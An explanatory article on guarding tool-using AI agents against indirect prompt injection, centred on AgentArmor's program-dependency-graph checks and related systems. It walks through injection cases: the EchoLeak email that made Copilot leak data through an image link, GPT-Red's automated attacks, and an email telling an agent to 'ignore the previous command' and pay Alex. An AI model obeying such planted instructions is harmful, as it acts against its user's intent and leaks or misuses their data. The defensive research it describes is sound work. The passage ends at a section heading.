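# Defending tool-using AI agents against prompt injection by checking their traces as program dependency graphs

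## How agents are hijacked, and the ideas borrowed from program analysis

An AI agent is a large language model that works in a loop, choosing a call to an external tool, reading the result, and choosing again until it has finished its task. The tools may search the web, open files, send email or move money. Because an agent acts on what it reads, an attacker can plant instructions in an email, file or web page, and the agent may carry them out with its user's permissions. This is called indirect prompt injection. Ling, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Secure LLM Agents*, surveyed 247 papers and found that prompt injection and the hijacking of tool calls still dominate research on agent security.

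Some defences train the model to resist planted instructions, or filter the text before the model reads it. Others check each action from outside before it takes effect, on the assumption that an attacker will sometimes fool the model. AgentArmor, which Wang, Liu and colleagues built at ByteDance (*AGENTARMOR*, 2025), takes this second approach. It treats the record of an agent's run like a program, works out which inputs led to which tool call, and blocks calls that break a rule. Its ideas long predate language models and come from compiler research on how one statement in a program depends on another, and from the security labels developed in military computing in the 1970s.

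### The agent loop and its single stream of text

Wang and colleagues break the loop into five steps. The agent first receives a system prompt, in which the developer describes its role and tools, and a user prompt with the task. The model may then generate a thought, which is its reasoning about what to do next (some providers hide this text, and some agents skip this step). Next, the model makes a tool call, which consists of a tool's name and its parameters. The surrounding software runs the tool and adds its output, called the observation, to the agent's context, which is all the text the model reads on the next pass. The loop starts again from the thought. The runtime trace is the record of the whole run.

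Suppose a user asks an agent to pay the bill in a file. On the first pass, the model generates a call that reads the file. On the second, it generates a payment call, using the amount and account number from the file. By then, the context contains text from the developer, the user and whoever wrote the file. If the file also contains an instruction to forward the user's address book to a stranger, that instruction is in the same context as the user's request.

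*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA, several universities and elsewhere, traces prompt injection to the way a language model processes trusted and untrusted text as one stream of tokens (word fragments), with no built-in separation between them. Other software solved the equivalent problem by separating commands from data. A database can accept a query separately from the values that go into it, so that it never interprets a value as a command, and a processor can mark regions of memory as data that it must not execute. A developer can imitate this by putting markers around outside text and training the model to treat everything between them as data. But this separation is only as good as the training, and the paper reports that persistent attackers have consistently got past it. Detectors that look for instructions inside data have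 also failed once attackers adapted to them.

Users often want an agent to follow instructions that it finds. If a user asks an agent to work through the to-do list in a shared document, the items on that list are legitimate commands, but the same items in an unsolicited email are an attack. No filter, however good, can tell these cases apart by wording alone, because they differ in where the text came from and what the user asked for.

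### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant built into Microsoft's office software, answers an employee's questions by retrieving relevant emails and files and adding them to the model's prompt. In January 2025, security researchers at Aim Labs found that an outsider could exploit this with a single email. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs the case. The email looked like ordinary business correspondence but contained instructions for Copilot. When the employee later asked about something confidential, Copilot could retrieve the email along with internal documents. The model then followed the email's instructions and wrote sensitive details into the address of an image in its answer. The employee's software fetched the image automatically, without a click, and the request carried the details to the attacker's server.

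Microsoft had protected this route with a classifier for injected prompts, a filter that removed outside links from answers, and a list of domains from which the software could load content. The attack got past all of them. Aim Labs reported the flaw privately, Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May 2025, and the public advisory followed in June. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had used the flaw against real victims, so EchoLeak was a demonstration rather than a breach. Reddy and Gujral nevertheless call it the first known case in which a prompt injection caused concrete data theft in a production system.

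Each protection checked one surface feature, such as the wording of the email or the domain of the link. None of them tracked the confidential text itself or detected that a stranger's email had caused it to leak. Other attacks exploit the same gap. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses eleven real attacks on agents, including ChatGPT, Claude Code and the coding agent Devin, and sorts them by the security principles they violated. The only principle violated in all eleven is secure information flow, which requires that sensitive data not reach places without the authority to receive it.

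### How well models resist in 2026

Training has made models much harder to hijack, with large gains in 2026. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes an attacking model trained by self-play. GPT-Red was rewarded for each injection that worked, while a collection of defender models was rewarded for resisting the injection and completing the original task. By the end of training, GPT-Red could break nearly every model OpenAI set it against, up to and including GPT-5.5. This supports a remark by Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, that GPT-Red consistently circumvented GPT-5.5's defences. In a set of indirect-injection scenarios targeting the older GPT-5.1, GPT-Red found a working attack in 84%, compared with 13% for human testers. A model that has withstood human testers may therefore be much more vulnerable than their results suggest.

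OpenAI then used GPT-Red's attacks to train its next model, GPT-5.6 Sol, which fails on only 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct injections. Direct injections arrive through the chat, but an agent is mainly exposed to text that arrives through its tools. Sol fails more often on attacks that arrive that way. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that OpenAI's August 2026 update put Sol's average failure rate on them at 3.77%.

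Anthropic likewise reports that, in tests of agent safety, Claude Opus 5 improved most over Opus 4.8 on prompt injection. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* cites a 0% attack success rate across 129 browser scenarios. *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026) reproduces results from a more general benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan, in which an attacker had a 0.2% chance of success against Opus 5 with one attempt and 2.0% within fifteen. The chance within fifteen attempts was 20.0% against GPT-5.6 Sol.

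At a success rate of 0.2%, a thousand emailed injections of the same quality would yield about two successes, and emails cost almost nothing to send. Most real attackers probably write worse injections than those in the benchmark, so the rate in ordinary use is presumably lower. Rates also vary enormously between models. iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* reports results from Gray Swan's *Frontier Hazard Tracker*, a public record of safety tests that appeared in late 2026. The success rate for prompt injection within fifteen attacks was 2.3% against Google's Gemini 4 Argon and 94.3% against Nvidia's Nemotron 3.5 Super VL, whose weights anyone can download. Developers who build agents on such a model cannot rely on it to refuse injected instructions.

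OpenAI calls robustness to prompt injection a hard, open problem. Google's *How Gemini’s defense-in-depth approach works* states that no detector catches every injection, which is why Google uses fixed rules outside the model to restrict the addresses Gemini can open. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* conjectures that persistent attackers will always evade defences that rely on the model to separate instructions from data, though the results for Opus 5 count somewhat against this. But a model with a very low failure rate can still fail, and an outside check aims to enforce a rule that holds whatever the model does.

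### Graphs of what depends on what

A check of this kind has to establish which inputs led to an action. Compiler writers faced a similar question when they wanted to rearrange a program without changing its results. Take a program of four lines that emails a user when a shop has run out of something:

```
1  addr = ask_user()
2  page = fetch(shop_site)
3  if "sold out" in page:
4      send_email(addr, "It is sold out")
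```

A control flow graph has a node for each statement and an arrow for each possible step of execution. Here execution runs from line 1 to 2 to 3, and from line 3 either to line 4 or to the end. A data flow graph has an arrow wherever one statement uses a value that another produced. Here line 3 uses the page from line 2, and line 4 uses the address from line 1.

In 1987, Ferrante, Ottenstein and Warren combined the two kinds of information in the program dependence graph (PDG), which the literature on agents tends to call the program dependency graph. It keeps the data arrows and replaces the order of execution with control dependencies. A statement is control-dependent on a branch if one outcome of the branch always leads to the statement and another can skip it. Line 4, for example, is control-dependent on line 3.

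| Graph | Arrows in the example |
|---|---|
| Control flow graph | 1→2, 2→3, 3→4, 3→end, 4→end |
| Data flow graph | 1→4 (`addr`), 2→3 (`page`) |
| Program dependency graph | 1→4 and 2→3 (data), 3→4 (control) |

The PDG no longer has an arrow from line 1 to line 2, because their order doesn't matter and a compiler could safely swap them. Following the arrows backwards from line 4 finds everything that can affect the email. A data dependency leads to line 1. A control dependency leads to line 3, and from there a data dependency leads to line 2. Programmers call this set of statements a slice.

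Taint tracking is a narrower analysis. It marks data from a suspect source, copies the mark to every value that a program computes from that data, and raises an alarm if a marked value reaches a sensitive operation. If the shop's page is the suspect source, a tracker that follows only data dependencies marks only `page`. It raises no alarm about the email in line 4 because both of the email's parameters are unmarked. Yet whoever runs the shop's site decides whether the email is sent. A tracker must also follow control dependencies to detect that influence.

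An injection can hijack an agent in two ways. It may change a parameter, such as the account number in a payment the user did ask for, or it may cause a call the user never asked for, even one whose parameters all come from trusted sources. In an ordinary program, the conditions that control what runs, such as `if` statements, are written in the source code. An agent's choice of tool happens inside the model and leaves no written condition to inspect, so AgentArmor has to infer the control dependencies in its graphs from the trace.

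### Labels and how they combine

Knowing what influenced a call is of little use without a way to judge those influences, which security labels provide. Bell and LaPadula, writing for the US military in the early 1970s, ordered data by secrecy. In their model, a process may not read data above its own clearance or write to a place below it, so secrets can move only towards equal or greater secrecy. In 1977, Biba reversed these rules to protect trusted data. Under Biba's rules, a trusted process may not read less trusted data, and an untrusted process may not write to trusted places. A confidentiality label records how restricted the audience for a piece of data is, and an integrity label records how far its origin can be trusted.

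Denning described the general structure in 1976. It consists of a set of labels, an ordering that determines which flows are permissible, and an operation, the join, that gives the label of a result from the labels of its inputs. The joined label is as secret as the most secret input and as untrusted as the least trusted one. With numbers this becomes simple arithmetic. Let secrecy run from 0 (public) to 2 (secret), and let distrust run from 0 (the user's own words) to 2 (a stranger's). The join takes the larger number in each column:

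(s₁, d₁) ⊔ (s₂, d₂) = (max(s₁, s₂), max(d₁, d₂))

| Data | Secrecy | Distrust |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | 1 | 0 |
| A payroll file that a colleague maintains | 2 | 1 |
| A public web page | 0 | 2 |
| A summary that draws on all three | 2 | 2 |

Each action then has a limit for each number, and data may enter the action only if neither of its numbers exceeds the action's limit. Posting on a public site might have the limits (0, 2), because the text may come from any source but must be public. A bank transfer might have the limits (2, 0), because a bank may see confidential details but only the user should determine them. The web page may go into the public post, and the user's request may go into the transfer, but the summary may go into neither. The ordering of labels is only partial. For example, the payroll file is more secret than the web page, but the web page is less trusted,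 so neither label is above the other.

Information-flow control means attaching labels to data, carrying them through a computation and checking them before an action. The strongest guarantee it aims for is noninterference, which means that changing untrusted inputs cannot alter a trusted output, and changing secret inputs cannot alter a public output.

The join also causes the main practical problem, known as label creep, in which restrictive labels spread until legitimate actions fail. Labels can only become more restrictive as data accumulates, and a language model mixes everything in its context, so a cautious system must assume that every observation influenced every later call. After one visit to a public web page, everything the agent produces has a distrust of 2, and the bank transfer stays blocked even if the page had no bearing on it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* identifies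 separating the sources mixed inside a model as the open research problem for information-flow control in agents. A dependency graph offers one way around label creep, because a call that depends only on the user's request can keep the request's label, provided the graph's arrows are correct.

### AgentDojo

A defence can fail by letting attacks through or by blocking legitimate work, so a test has to measure both. Most of the work on outside checks uses AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2024. It simulates four settings, each with its own tools and data: an office workspace with email and calendar, the messaging service Slack, a bank and a travel agency. The original release contains 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill or summarising a message. It also contains injection tasks, which are the attacker's goals. The benchmark places the attack text in data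 that the agent's tools return.

A security case pairs one user task with one injection task from the same suite. Zhou and colleagues describe the Slack suite as having 21 user tasks and 5 injection tasks, which makes 105 cases. The four suites together have 629 cases.

AgentDojo uses code rather than a language model to determine whether an attack succeeded. Each task comes with a short piece of code that examines the simulated environment after the run and tests, for instance, whether money went to the attacker's account. The attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the attacker's goal was achieved, so an injection that merely confuses the agent does not count. The checks are repeatable but can be wrong. Zhou and colleagues found that the check for one injection task wrongly registered a success in 29 of their 2,940 runs, which they reviewed by hand.

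Utility without attack is the share of user tasks that the agent completes with no injection present, measured over 21 runs in the Slack suite. Utility under attack is the share of the 105 paired runs in which the agent still completes the user's task with an injection present. The two can differ widely. A defence that ends the whole run at the first suspicious call may have excellent utility without attack and a very low attack success rate, but very low utility under attack, and an attacker could then stop the agent's work at will. A defence that removes only the injected call and lets the agent continue would do well on all three measures. Attack success rate alone is little use for judging a defence, since an agent that never does anything gets the best possible score, zero.

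AgentDojo has become a weaker test of security with age. Zhou and colleagues ran four models on its Slack suite (Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, GPT-5.4 and Sonnet 5), and all of them resisted all 105 attacks with no policy in force. With such models, the standard attacks cannot show whether a defence adds any protection. Zhou and colleagues therefore gave the injection as the only instruction to the part of the agent that read it, which simulates a model that the attacker has already hijacked. Results based on AgentDojo's standard attacks, including AgentArmor's, depend heavily on how easily those attacks fooled the underlying model.

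## Turning a runtime trace into a dependency graph

AgentArmor sits between the agent and its tools. When the model generates a tool call, AgentArmor holds the call, adds it to a graph of the run so far, and checks the graph before the tool can run. A component called the graph constructor builds this graph. The attacks AgentArmor can catch depend on what the constructor represents and on what Wang and colleagues assume about the attacker.

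### The threat model

In the threat model, the attacker can reach the agent only through content it reads while doing the user's task, such as an email or web page. The attacker knows which tools the agent has and roughly how it reasons, and can plant content that takes effect over several passes of the agent's loop. The defender is whoever deploys the agent. They can't control what the agent reads or predict how an attacker will word an injection, but they control the software around the model, so they can inspect the chosen tool, its parameters and any visible reasoning before a call runs.

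Wang and colleagues also assume that tools are honest and that the model is trusted. An honest tool behaves as described and reports its results accurately, so an email tool that faithfully returns a malicious email still counts as honest. AgentArmor does not protect against a tampered tool that invents its output. A trusted model has no hidden behaviour planted during training, though injected text can still fool it.

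The graph covers only actions that pass through tools. It has no node for the agent's decision to stop, and Wang and colleagues acknowledge that AgentArmor therefore can't handle denial-of-service attacks, in which an injection keeps the agent from finishing its work. It also has no node for the agent's final answer. This matters for EchoLeak, one of Wang and colleagues' motivating cases, because the confidential details leaked through an image link in Copilot's answer. To cover such an attack, an operator would probably have to treat displaying an answer as a tool call.

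### Nodes and edges

AgentArmor builds a control flow graph and a data flow graph, then merges parts of both into a program dependency graph (PDG). Nine types of node appear across the three:

| Node type | What it represents | Control flow | Data flow | PDG |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| System prompt | The developer's instructions | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| User prompt | The user's request | Yes | Yes | Yes |
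| Model call | One pass through the language model | Yes | No | No |
| Thought | The model's reasoning text | Yes | No | No |
| Tool name | The choice of a particular tool | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Tool parameter | One value passed to the tool | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Tool | The tool itself | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Observation | The tool's output | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Data | A file, database or other item that a tool uses | No | Yes | Yes |

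AgentArmor splits a single tool call into several nodes because different inputs may have determined different parts of it. Suppose a user asks an agent to send a reminder to a meeting's attendees, and the agent looks up their addresses before calling the email tool. The user's request led to the choice of tool, but the lookup supplied the recipients. If the call were one node, both dependencies would point to it, and this legitimate call would look much like a hijacked one. AgentArmor instead draws a control dependency from the user prompt to the tool name, and a data dependency from the observation returned by the lookup to the recipient parameter.

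Data and control dependencies differ in what would have changed if an input had been different. If a different observation would have changed the parameter but not the tool, the parameter has a data dependency on the observation, and the tool name has no control dependency on it.

The control flow graph has two types of edge. Control flow edges record the order of events, and control dependency edges link a prompt or observation to the tool name it led to. The data flow graph has three types. Input edges run from a parameter to its tool, output edges run from a tool to its observation, and data dependency edges link a value to its source, or a folder to the files in it. The PDG combines the two graphs but leaves out the control flow edges.

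### From the trace to the finished graph

Wang and colleagues illustrate the construction with an agent that manages email. The agent can search emails with `search_email` and make payments with `create_trans`. The system prompt tells it to use only email tools. The user asks for emails from Alex, and the agent calls `search_email` with the sender set to "Alex". One of the returned emails contains an instruction to ignore the previous command and pay Alex 10 dollars. The model follows the instruction and generates a call to `create_trans`.

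The constructor first turns the trace into a control flow graph. It adds a node for each prompt, model call, thought, tool call and observation, and connects them in the order they occurred. This takes no judgement, because the trace already records the order. The graph shows that the payment call came after the email search, but not why the agent made it.

AgentArmor next adds the control dependencies. Its dependency analyser, a language model, uses the earlier prompts and observations and the agent's reasoning to identify the inputs that caused each call. In this example, it attributes the choice of `search_email` to the user's request and the choice of `create_trans` to the observation containing the email. The constructor also splits each call into its tool name and parameters.

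The constructor then starts the data flow graph by copying the nodes that carry data and leaving out the model calls and thoughts. Wang and colleagues describe the omitted nodes as purely logical elements, which understates the effect of omitting them. If the graph kept the model calls, it would need an arrow into each one from everything in the context, which would cause label creep. Without them, the graph has no connection between what the agent read and what it did next, so the analyser has to supply one.

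The defense turns a runtime trace into a dependency graph by inferring data dependencies. In one example, it traces the sender "Alex" in a search to the user's request, and the payment's receiver and amount to an email.

Some data flows never appear in a trace, so the constructor also uses the property registry, a store of facts about tools and data. For instance, when an agent clones a code repository, the observation may contain only a message that the command finished. The registry's entry for the tool records that data flows from the repository's address to a new folder on the local disk. The constructor adds a node for that folder and can link it to the files inside, so if the agent later reads one of them, the graph can connect it to the outside repository it came from. In the email example, the constructor adds a node for the stored emails, `email_data`.

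In their main description of the method, Wang and colleagues add the registry's data before inferring data dependencies, but in the worked example they add it afterwards. The order shouldn't affect the result, because the analyser considers only prompts and observations as possible sources of a parameter.

Finally, the constructor merges the two graphs. It takes all the edges of the data flow graph and adds the control dependencies:

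| From | To | Type of edge | Basis |
|---|---|---|---|
| User prompt | `search_email` (name) | Control dependency | Inferred |
| User prompt | `sender="Alex"` | Data dependency | Inferred |
| `sender="Alex"` | `search_email` (tool) | Input | Trace |
| `email_data` | `search_email` (tool) | Input | Registry |
| `search_email` (tool) | Observation | Output | Trace |
| Observation | `create_trans` (name) | Control dependency | Inferred |
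| Observation | `receiver="Alex"` | Data dependency | Inferred |
| Observation | `amount="10$"` | Data dependency | Inferred |
| `receiver`, `amount` | `create_trans` (tool) | Input | Trace |

Wang and colleagues list the five inferred edges, and the others follow from their construction rules. The payment tool has no observation because it has not run. AgentArmor checks the graph at this point using security labels on the nodes and blocks the payment.

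The analyser needs some understanding of the text to identify where the payment's receiver came from. "Alex" appears in both the user's request and the malicious email, so a tracker that only matched strings could trace the receiver to the user and treat it as trustworthy. The analyser has to recognise that the user mentioned Alex only as a sender of emails.

It is also not enough to check whether a call traces back to the user, because the user's request started the run and most calls will have some path back to it. The payment's path runs backwards through the observation, the search tool and the sender parameter to the user's request. The payment differs from a legitimate call in that both the choice of tool and its parameters come from a stranger's text.

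### How far a trace resembles a program

Wang and colleagues justify their approach by matching the parts of a trace to the parts of a program. A tool call corresponds to a function call, an observation to the value the function returns, and the model's reasoning to the logic inside a function that turns inputs into outputs. The match is good for tool calls, which have names, parameters and results as function calls do, but much weaker for control dependencies.

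A compiler works out the control dependencies in a PDG from all the paths that execution could take. The graph of the earlier shop program therefore has an edge from the "sold out" test to the email, even on runs where no email goes out.

Now suppose an agent does the same job and the page doesn't contain those words. The trace shows that the agent fetched the page and then finished. Because the trace records only the path the agent took, a graph built from it has no node for the email and no edge leading to it, even though the shop's page determined that the user would hear nothing. If an attacker persuades an agent *not* to send a warning, AgentArmor has no call to check.

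Even on the path taken, a control dependency in AgentArmor's graph is only the analyser's claim about what caused a call. The cause is hardest to identify when the user's own request contains a condition. In one of Wang and colleagues' examples, a user asks the agent to reschedule an airport pickup if the flight is more than two hours late, and otherwise to confirm the pickup. The agent finds a three-hour delay and reschedules. In a program, both calls would be control-dependent on a test of the delay, and the test would depend on the flight data. AgentArmor's graph has no node for the test, so the analyser must attach the rescheduling call to the user's request, to the flight data, or to both.

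A different delay would have led to a different tool, so by Wang and colleagues' definition there should be a control dependency between the flight data and the call. If the analyser records that dependency, a source outside the user's control appears to be directing the agent, and a strict rule might block a call the user asked for. If it records only the user's request as the cause, the call goes through, but anyone who can falsify the flight data can switch the agent between the two actions without the graph showing their influence. Missing that influence seems less serious than blocking the call, because the user authorised both actions, but it could still be costly if one of them were a large purchase.

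These limits also prevent the graph from establishing noninterference, because that guarantee compares different runs. A graph of one run contains no information about what would have happened in another, except for what the analyser guesses.

Compiler research has a closer counterpart to AgentArmor's graph, the dynamic dependence graph, which Agrawal and Horgan described in 1990. Its nodes are statements that actually executed, so it too describes a single run. *GRADE* (Zhao, 2026) places graphs of agent runs in a line of work that includes these graphs and dynamic slicing, which Korel and Laski introduced in 1988. For an ordinary program, an analyser can derive the edges from the source code and a record of the execution, but the part of an agent that makes the decisions has no readable source code.

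Zhao proposes grading each dependency edge by the evidence for it. An edge is observed if the trace shows the access, declared if extra logging recorded it, and inferred if it rests on an assumption. In AgentArmor's graph, the edges from tools to their outputs are observed. The registry's edges are closest to declared, though they come from a general description of the tool rather than a log of the particular run. Nearly all the edges that expose an attack are inferred.

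Some evidence suggests that a dependency graph can seem informative even when its arrows point to the wrong steps. Zhao used graphs from six collections of agent runs to predict which runs would fail at their task. On SWE-Gym, a collection of software engineering runs, a model given only the size of each run scored 0.663, on a scale where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. Adding four summary measures of the dependency graph raised the score to 0.804. Zhao then rewired the graphs, keeping the number of earlier steps each step depended on but changing which ones. With the rewired graphs, the model scored 0.811. After statistical correction, the real graphs did not clearly beat the rewired ones on any of the six collections.

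This suggests that good overall results are weak evidence that individual edges are correct. Wang and colleagues counted attacks stopped and tasks completed, but didn't score the edges. The finding isn't direct evidence against AgentArmor, because predicting failure is a different task from detecting an attack, and the rewiring couldn't alter two of the four summary measures.

### What "static" means here

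Wang and colleagues describe AgentArmor's type system as performing static inference and checking. Static analysis normally examines a program without running it and aims to reach conclusions that hold for every possible run. AgentArmor's check is static only in the weaker sense that it examines a fixed graph before the pending call takes effect. That graph describes one run up to that moment, and AgentArmor extends it at each step. "Runtime monitoring" would be a more accurate description, since a developer could not use the check before release to show that an agent will never make an unauthorised payment.

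Because AgentArmor works at run time, it can check the actual tool, receiver and amount, and doesn't have to warn about combinations that the agent might never produce. Three systems from 2026 instead build the graph from source code or old logs.

### AgentFlow

*AgentFlow* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026), a separate project led from Huazhong University of Science and Technology, builds dependency graphs from an agent's source code. Developers often write agents with frameworks such as LangGraph or CrewAI, which supply ready-made components for prompts, tools and memory. A developer may give an agent access to email by including the email tool in a list. An ordinary code analyser would identify this only as a list passed to a function. AgentFlow, which has rules for 143 such constructs in five frameworks, turns it into an edge from the agent to the tool.

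One AgentFlow example has two agents with a shared memory. A research agent can search the web and hand work over to an operations agent, which can send email after an approval step. The models decide at run time whether the first agent hands over its work and whether the second sends anything, so AgentFlow's graph deliberately includes every transfer that the code permits, even those that may never happen. AgentArmor's graph includes only what has happened.

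To find risky programs, AgentFlow searches for triples (*p*, *a*, *c*) of a prompt, an agent and a sensitive tool that meet three conditions:

- data can flow from *p* to *a*, possibly through other agents;
- control can pass from *a* to *c*;
- *a* can supply the arguments of *c*.

AgentFlow assumes that any prompt reaching an agent could influence any call the agent makes, rather than trying to work out what the model would do with the prompt. It therefore doesn't need a language model to judge what caused a call, but an operator who applied this assumption to live calls would block far too many of them.

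Among 5,399 real agent programs, AgentFlow flagged 238, or 4.4%. The most common risk, found in 129 programs, was that a prompt could lead the agent to send something outside. Two of the researchers checked 100 of the reports by hand and judged 73 correct. In 25 of the 27 false reports, the path from prompt to tool was real, but the tool was less dangerous than AgentFlow had rated it (for example, it could only read files). The researchers also examined 100 agents that had powerful tools but no report, and found nine that AgentFlow should have flagged. A developer can use these results to add an approval step or remove a tool before release, but not to determine whether an injection caused a particular email.

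### Beyond Predefined Sinks

AgentFlow's false reports show that a path to a powerful tool isn't necessarily dangerous. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (Cui, 2026), an October preprint that has not been peer reviewed, addresses this problem with a system called AgentSecGraph. AgentSecGraph also reads source code, but it builds a separate small graph around each sensitive operation, such as running a command or deleting a file.

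Cui illustrates the idea with three tools that all run a command. The first passes the agent's input straight to the command. The second overwrites the input with a fixed value, so the agent can't influence what runs. The third checks the input against a list of permitted values before passing it on. A scanner that looks only for commands can't distinguish these tools. AgentSecGraph records the input's source, its path to the operation and any check along the way. The edge names begin with "may", as in `may_guard`, because finding a check in the code doesn't prove that it works.

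AgentSecGraph found 23,866 sensitive operations in 67 code repositories. It found evidence that an outside or agent-supplied input could reach the operation in 41.15% of these operations, and evidence of a possible safeguard in 12.88%. These figures partly reflect the limits of the analyser and are not estimates of how many agents are vulnerable. The analyser found a dependency for 84.14% of operations that write files but only 1.87% of those that control a browser, and it analyses Python much more thoroughly than JavaScript.

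Cui also reproduced 22 sensitive behaviours under controlled conditions. One was a confirmed vulnerability, one was still awaiting disclosure, and 20 had protections or usage limits that kept them from counting as vulnerabilities. The 22 were not a random sample, so the proportion may not hold more generally. Still, the result supports the view that a security judgement can start from a dependency graph but also needs facts about trust and safeguards. AgentArmor gets such facts from its registry.

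### AgentTracer

*AgentTracer* (Yao, Wu and colleagues, October 2026) builds its graph after an attack has succeeded. An investigator starts with a suspicious call in the logs and uses AgentTracer to look for both the text that caused it and every other call the attacker induced.

In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to download a software release from a web page and upload it to GitHub. The page contains an injection that makes the agent register the attacker's access key, fetch emails, verify an account and clear its own memory. Between these steps, the agent continues the user's task. The calls that fetch emails and clear the memory take no parameters, so a graph that links calls only through shared data would leave them disconnected from the rest of the attack.

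AgentTracer therefore uses the agent's recorded reasoning to link calls by purpose. Its nodes are the user's request and the objects that tools bring in or change, such as web pages and files. Each edge is a triple (*nᵢ*, *o*, *nⱼ*), in which object *nᵢ* informed the decision to perform operation *o*, which introduced object *nⱼ*. A tool call is thus an edge, rather than a group of nodes as in AgentArmor's graph, and a path is a sequence of calls that serve one goal. AgentTracer marks the operations that the user's request doesn't authorise and follows the marked edges backwards from the suspicious call. If they end at an outside source, it reports that source as the injection.

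Yao and colleagues hid attack logs among 1,800 normal requests and 9,000 harmless tool calls. AgentTracer found the exact log line where the injection entered in 94.17% of cases, and 93.56% of the calls it assigned to the attacks were part of them. When the team replaced the links by purpose with links between consecutive calls, the share of malicious calls that AgentTracer found fell from 90.32% to 58.54%. The method needs reasoning text in the logs, so it is much less suited to agents whose providers hide that text.

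Yao and colleagues count AgentArmor among the methods that follow explicit dependencies, but their objection to such methods only partly applies to it. AgentArmor can draw a control dependency from the web page to the call that clears the memory, even though that call has no parameters. Their own comparison on 100 attacks is consistent with this:

| Method | Injection located | Malicious calls recovered | Recovered calls that were malicious |
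|---|---|---|---|
| AgentArmor | 76% | 94.10% | 53.62% |
| AgentTracer | 94% | 88.07% | 93.18% |

AgentArmor recovered more of the malicious calls than AgentTracer did, but nearly half of the calls it assigned to the attacks were harmless. These results come from a competing project, which rebuilt any method that lacked a complete public implementation, so ByteDance's own version might do better. The test also used AgentArmor to investigate past attacks, which Wang and colleagues did not design it to do. In live use, wrongly linking a harmless call to an attacker's text would block the call only if the link also made the call break a rule.

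## Deciding which input caused which action

A language model computes each output token from every token in its context. Removing an unrelated email from the context would therefore change the probability of the next tool call at least slightly, and an outside observer cannot tell which of these small influences matter. Sound tracking must never miss an influence, so it has to draw an edge to each tool call from everything the model had read before making it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) describes this rule as sound but possibly overly conservative. The rule leads to label creep, and the resulting graph would contain no more information than a chronological list of events.

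A more useful graph has to leave out the influences that don't matter, but it is hard to tell which those are. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (2026) addresses the same problem in ordinary programs that call a language model. It sorts the ways an input can reach the model's output into 25 categories. Some inputs survive only as a yes-or-no decision or a category name, and some have no observable effect. Since no one can observe the flow inside the model, the paper estimates these categories from labellers' judgements instead of deriving them from code.

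Defences for agents also rely on estimates. AgentArmor asks a language model what caused a call, while other systems measure attention inside a model or remove parts of the context and measure the change. These methods differ in accuracy and in what happens when an estimate is wrong.

### AgentArmor's dependency analyser

For each new tool call, AgentArmor fills in a prompt template with the user's prompt, the observations so far, the agent's thought and the call itself. Wang and colleagues also list the system prompt in their main text, but the template they print has no place for it. The template defines control and data dependencies and includes the question of which inputs led to the call. In the template's example, a user asks for a room to be booked, and an observation contains an instruction to cancel one. The user's prompt is the cause if the agent books a room, and the observation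 is the cause if it cancels one.

The analyser returns an explanation and a list of root causes, which may include numbered observations, the user's prompt or both. AgentArmor uses this list to draw the graph's edges. The format has no field for confidence, so a guess produces the same edge as an obvious answer.

The template also includes warnings about two mistakes. When an agent looks up today's date to book lunch, the date supplies a parameter but does not cause the booking. When the user sets a condition that affects only a parameter, the control dependency should still lead to the user's prompt. The second warning does not apply to the airport pickup example, because the condition there determines which of two tools the agent uses.

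Wang and colleagues report that they also gave the analyser seven patterns of agent reasoning, although the printed template covers only the two special cases. The patterns are:

- Direct user request: the user names an action, such as booking a table, and the agent performs it.
- Indirect execution: the agent adds a step that the user didn't mention, such as finding today's date before listing today's events.
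- Parameterised execution: the user's request determines the tool, and an observation supplies a parameter, such as an email address.
- Functional execution: the agent works out a parameter from raw data, such as the highest-rated hotel in a list.
- Conditional execution: the agent's action depends on whether a condition holds.
- Transfer execution: the user tells the agent to follow instructions in another source, such as a README file.
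- Multiple source execution: two or more independent sources call for the same action.

Even a correct edge may not be enough to decide whether a call should run. In transfer execution, an edge to the README shows where the instruction came from, but not whether the user asked the agent to follow it.

### What a wrong edge costs

Take the payment of 10 dollars to Alex, and suppose a rule permits payments only if the choice of tool and both parameters have high integrity. The user's prompt has high integrity and the emails have low integrity. The outcome then depends on what the user asked for and on what the analyser reports:

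| The user asked the agent to | Causes reported by the analyser | Integrity of the call | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Find Alex's emails | Email, for the tool and both parameters | Low | Injected payment blocked |
| Find Alex's emails | User's prompt, for all three | High | Injected payment goes through |
| Find Alex's emails and pay him 10 dollars | User's prompt, for all three | High | Requested payment goes through |
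| Find Alex's emails and pay him 10 dollars | User's prompt for the tool and receiver, email for the amount | Low | Requested payment blocked |

The second row shows a missed edge. The analyser traces no part of the payment to the email, so the payment gets the user's high integrity and the rule allows it. The rule would still block the payment if the analyser wrongly traced the receiver to the user's prompt but correctly traced the amount to the email.

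The last row contains a false edge. Perhaps one of the emails mentions a debt of 10 dollars, and the analyser wrongly identifies it as the source of the amount, which the user had already specified. One wrong edge is enough to block the payment. AgentArmor stops the whole run when it finds a violation, so the user may also lose the rest of the task.

The join makes the two errors asymmetric. If the analyser lists both the user's prompt and the email as causes, the result still has low integrity, so an attacker gains nothing by adding a trusted source and has to get the analyser to leave out the untrusted one. An operator could guard against this by having the analyser report every observation that might have contributed, but that would produce more false edges and, in the extreme case, link every call to the whole context again.

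In the comparison by Yao and colleagues, AgentArmor attributed many harmless calls to attacks, which suggests that false edges are the more frequent problem, at least in the version they tested. They are the safer kind of error, but they can make the agent abandon a user's work.

### Misleading the analyser on purpose

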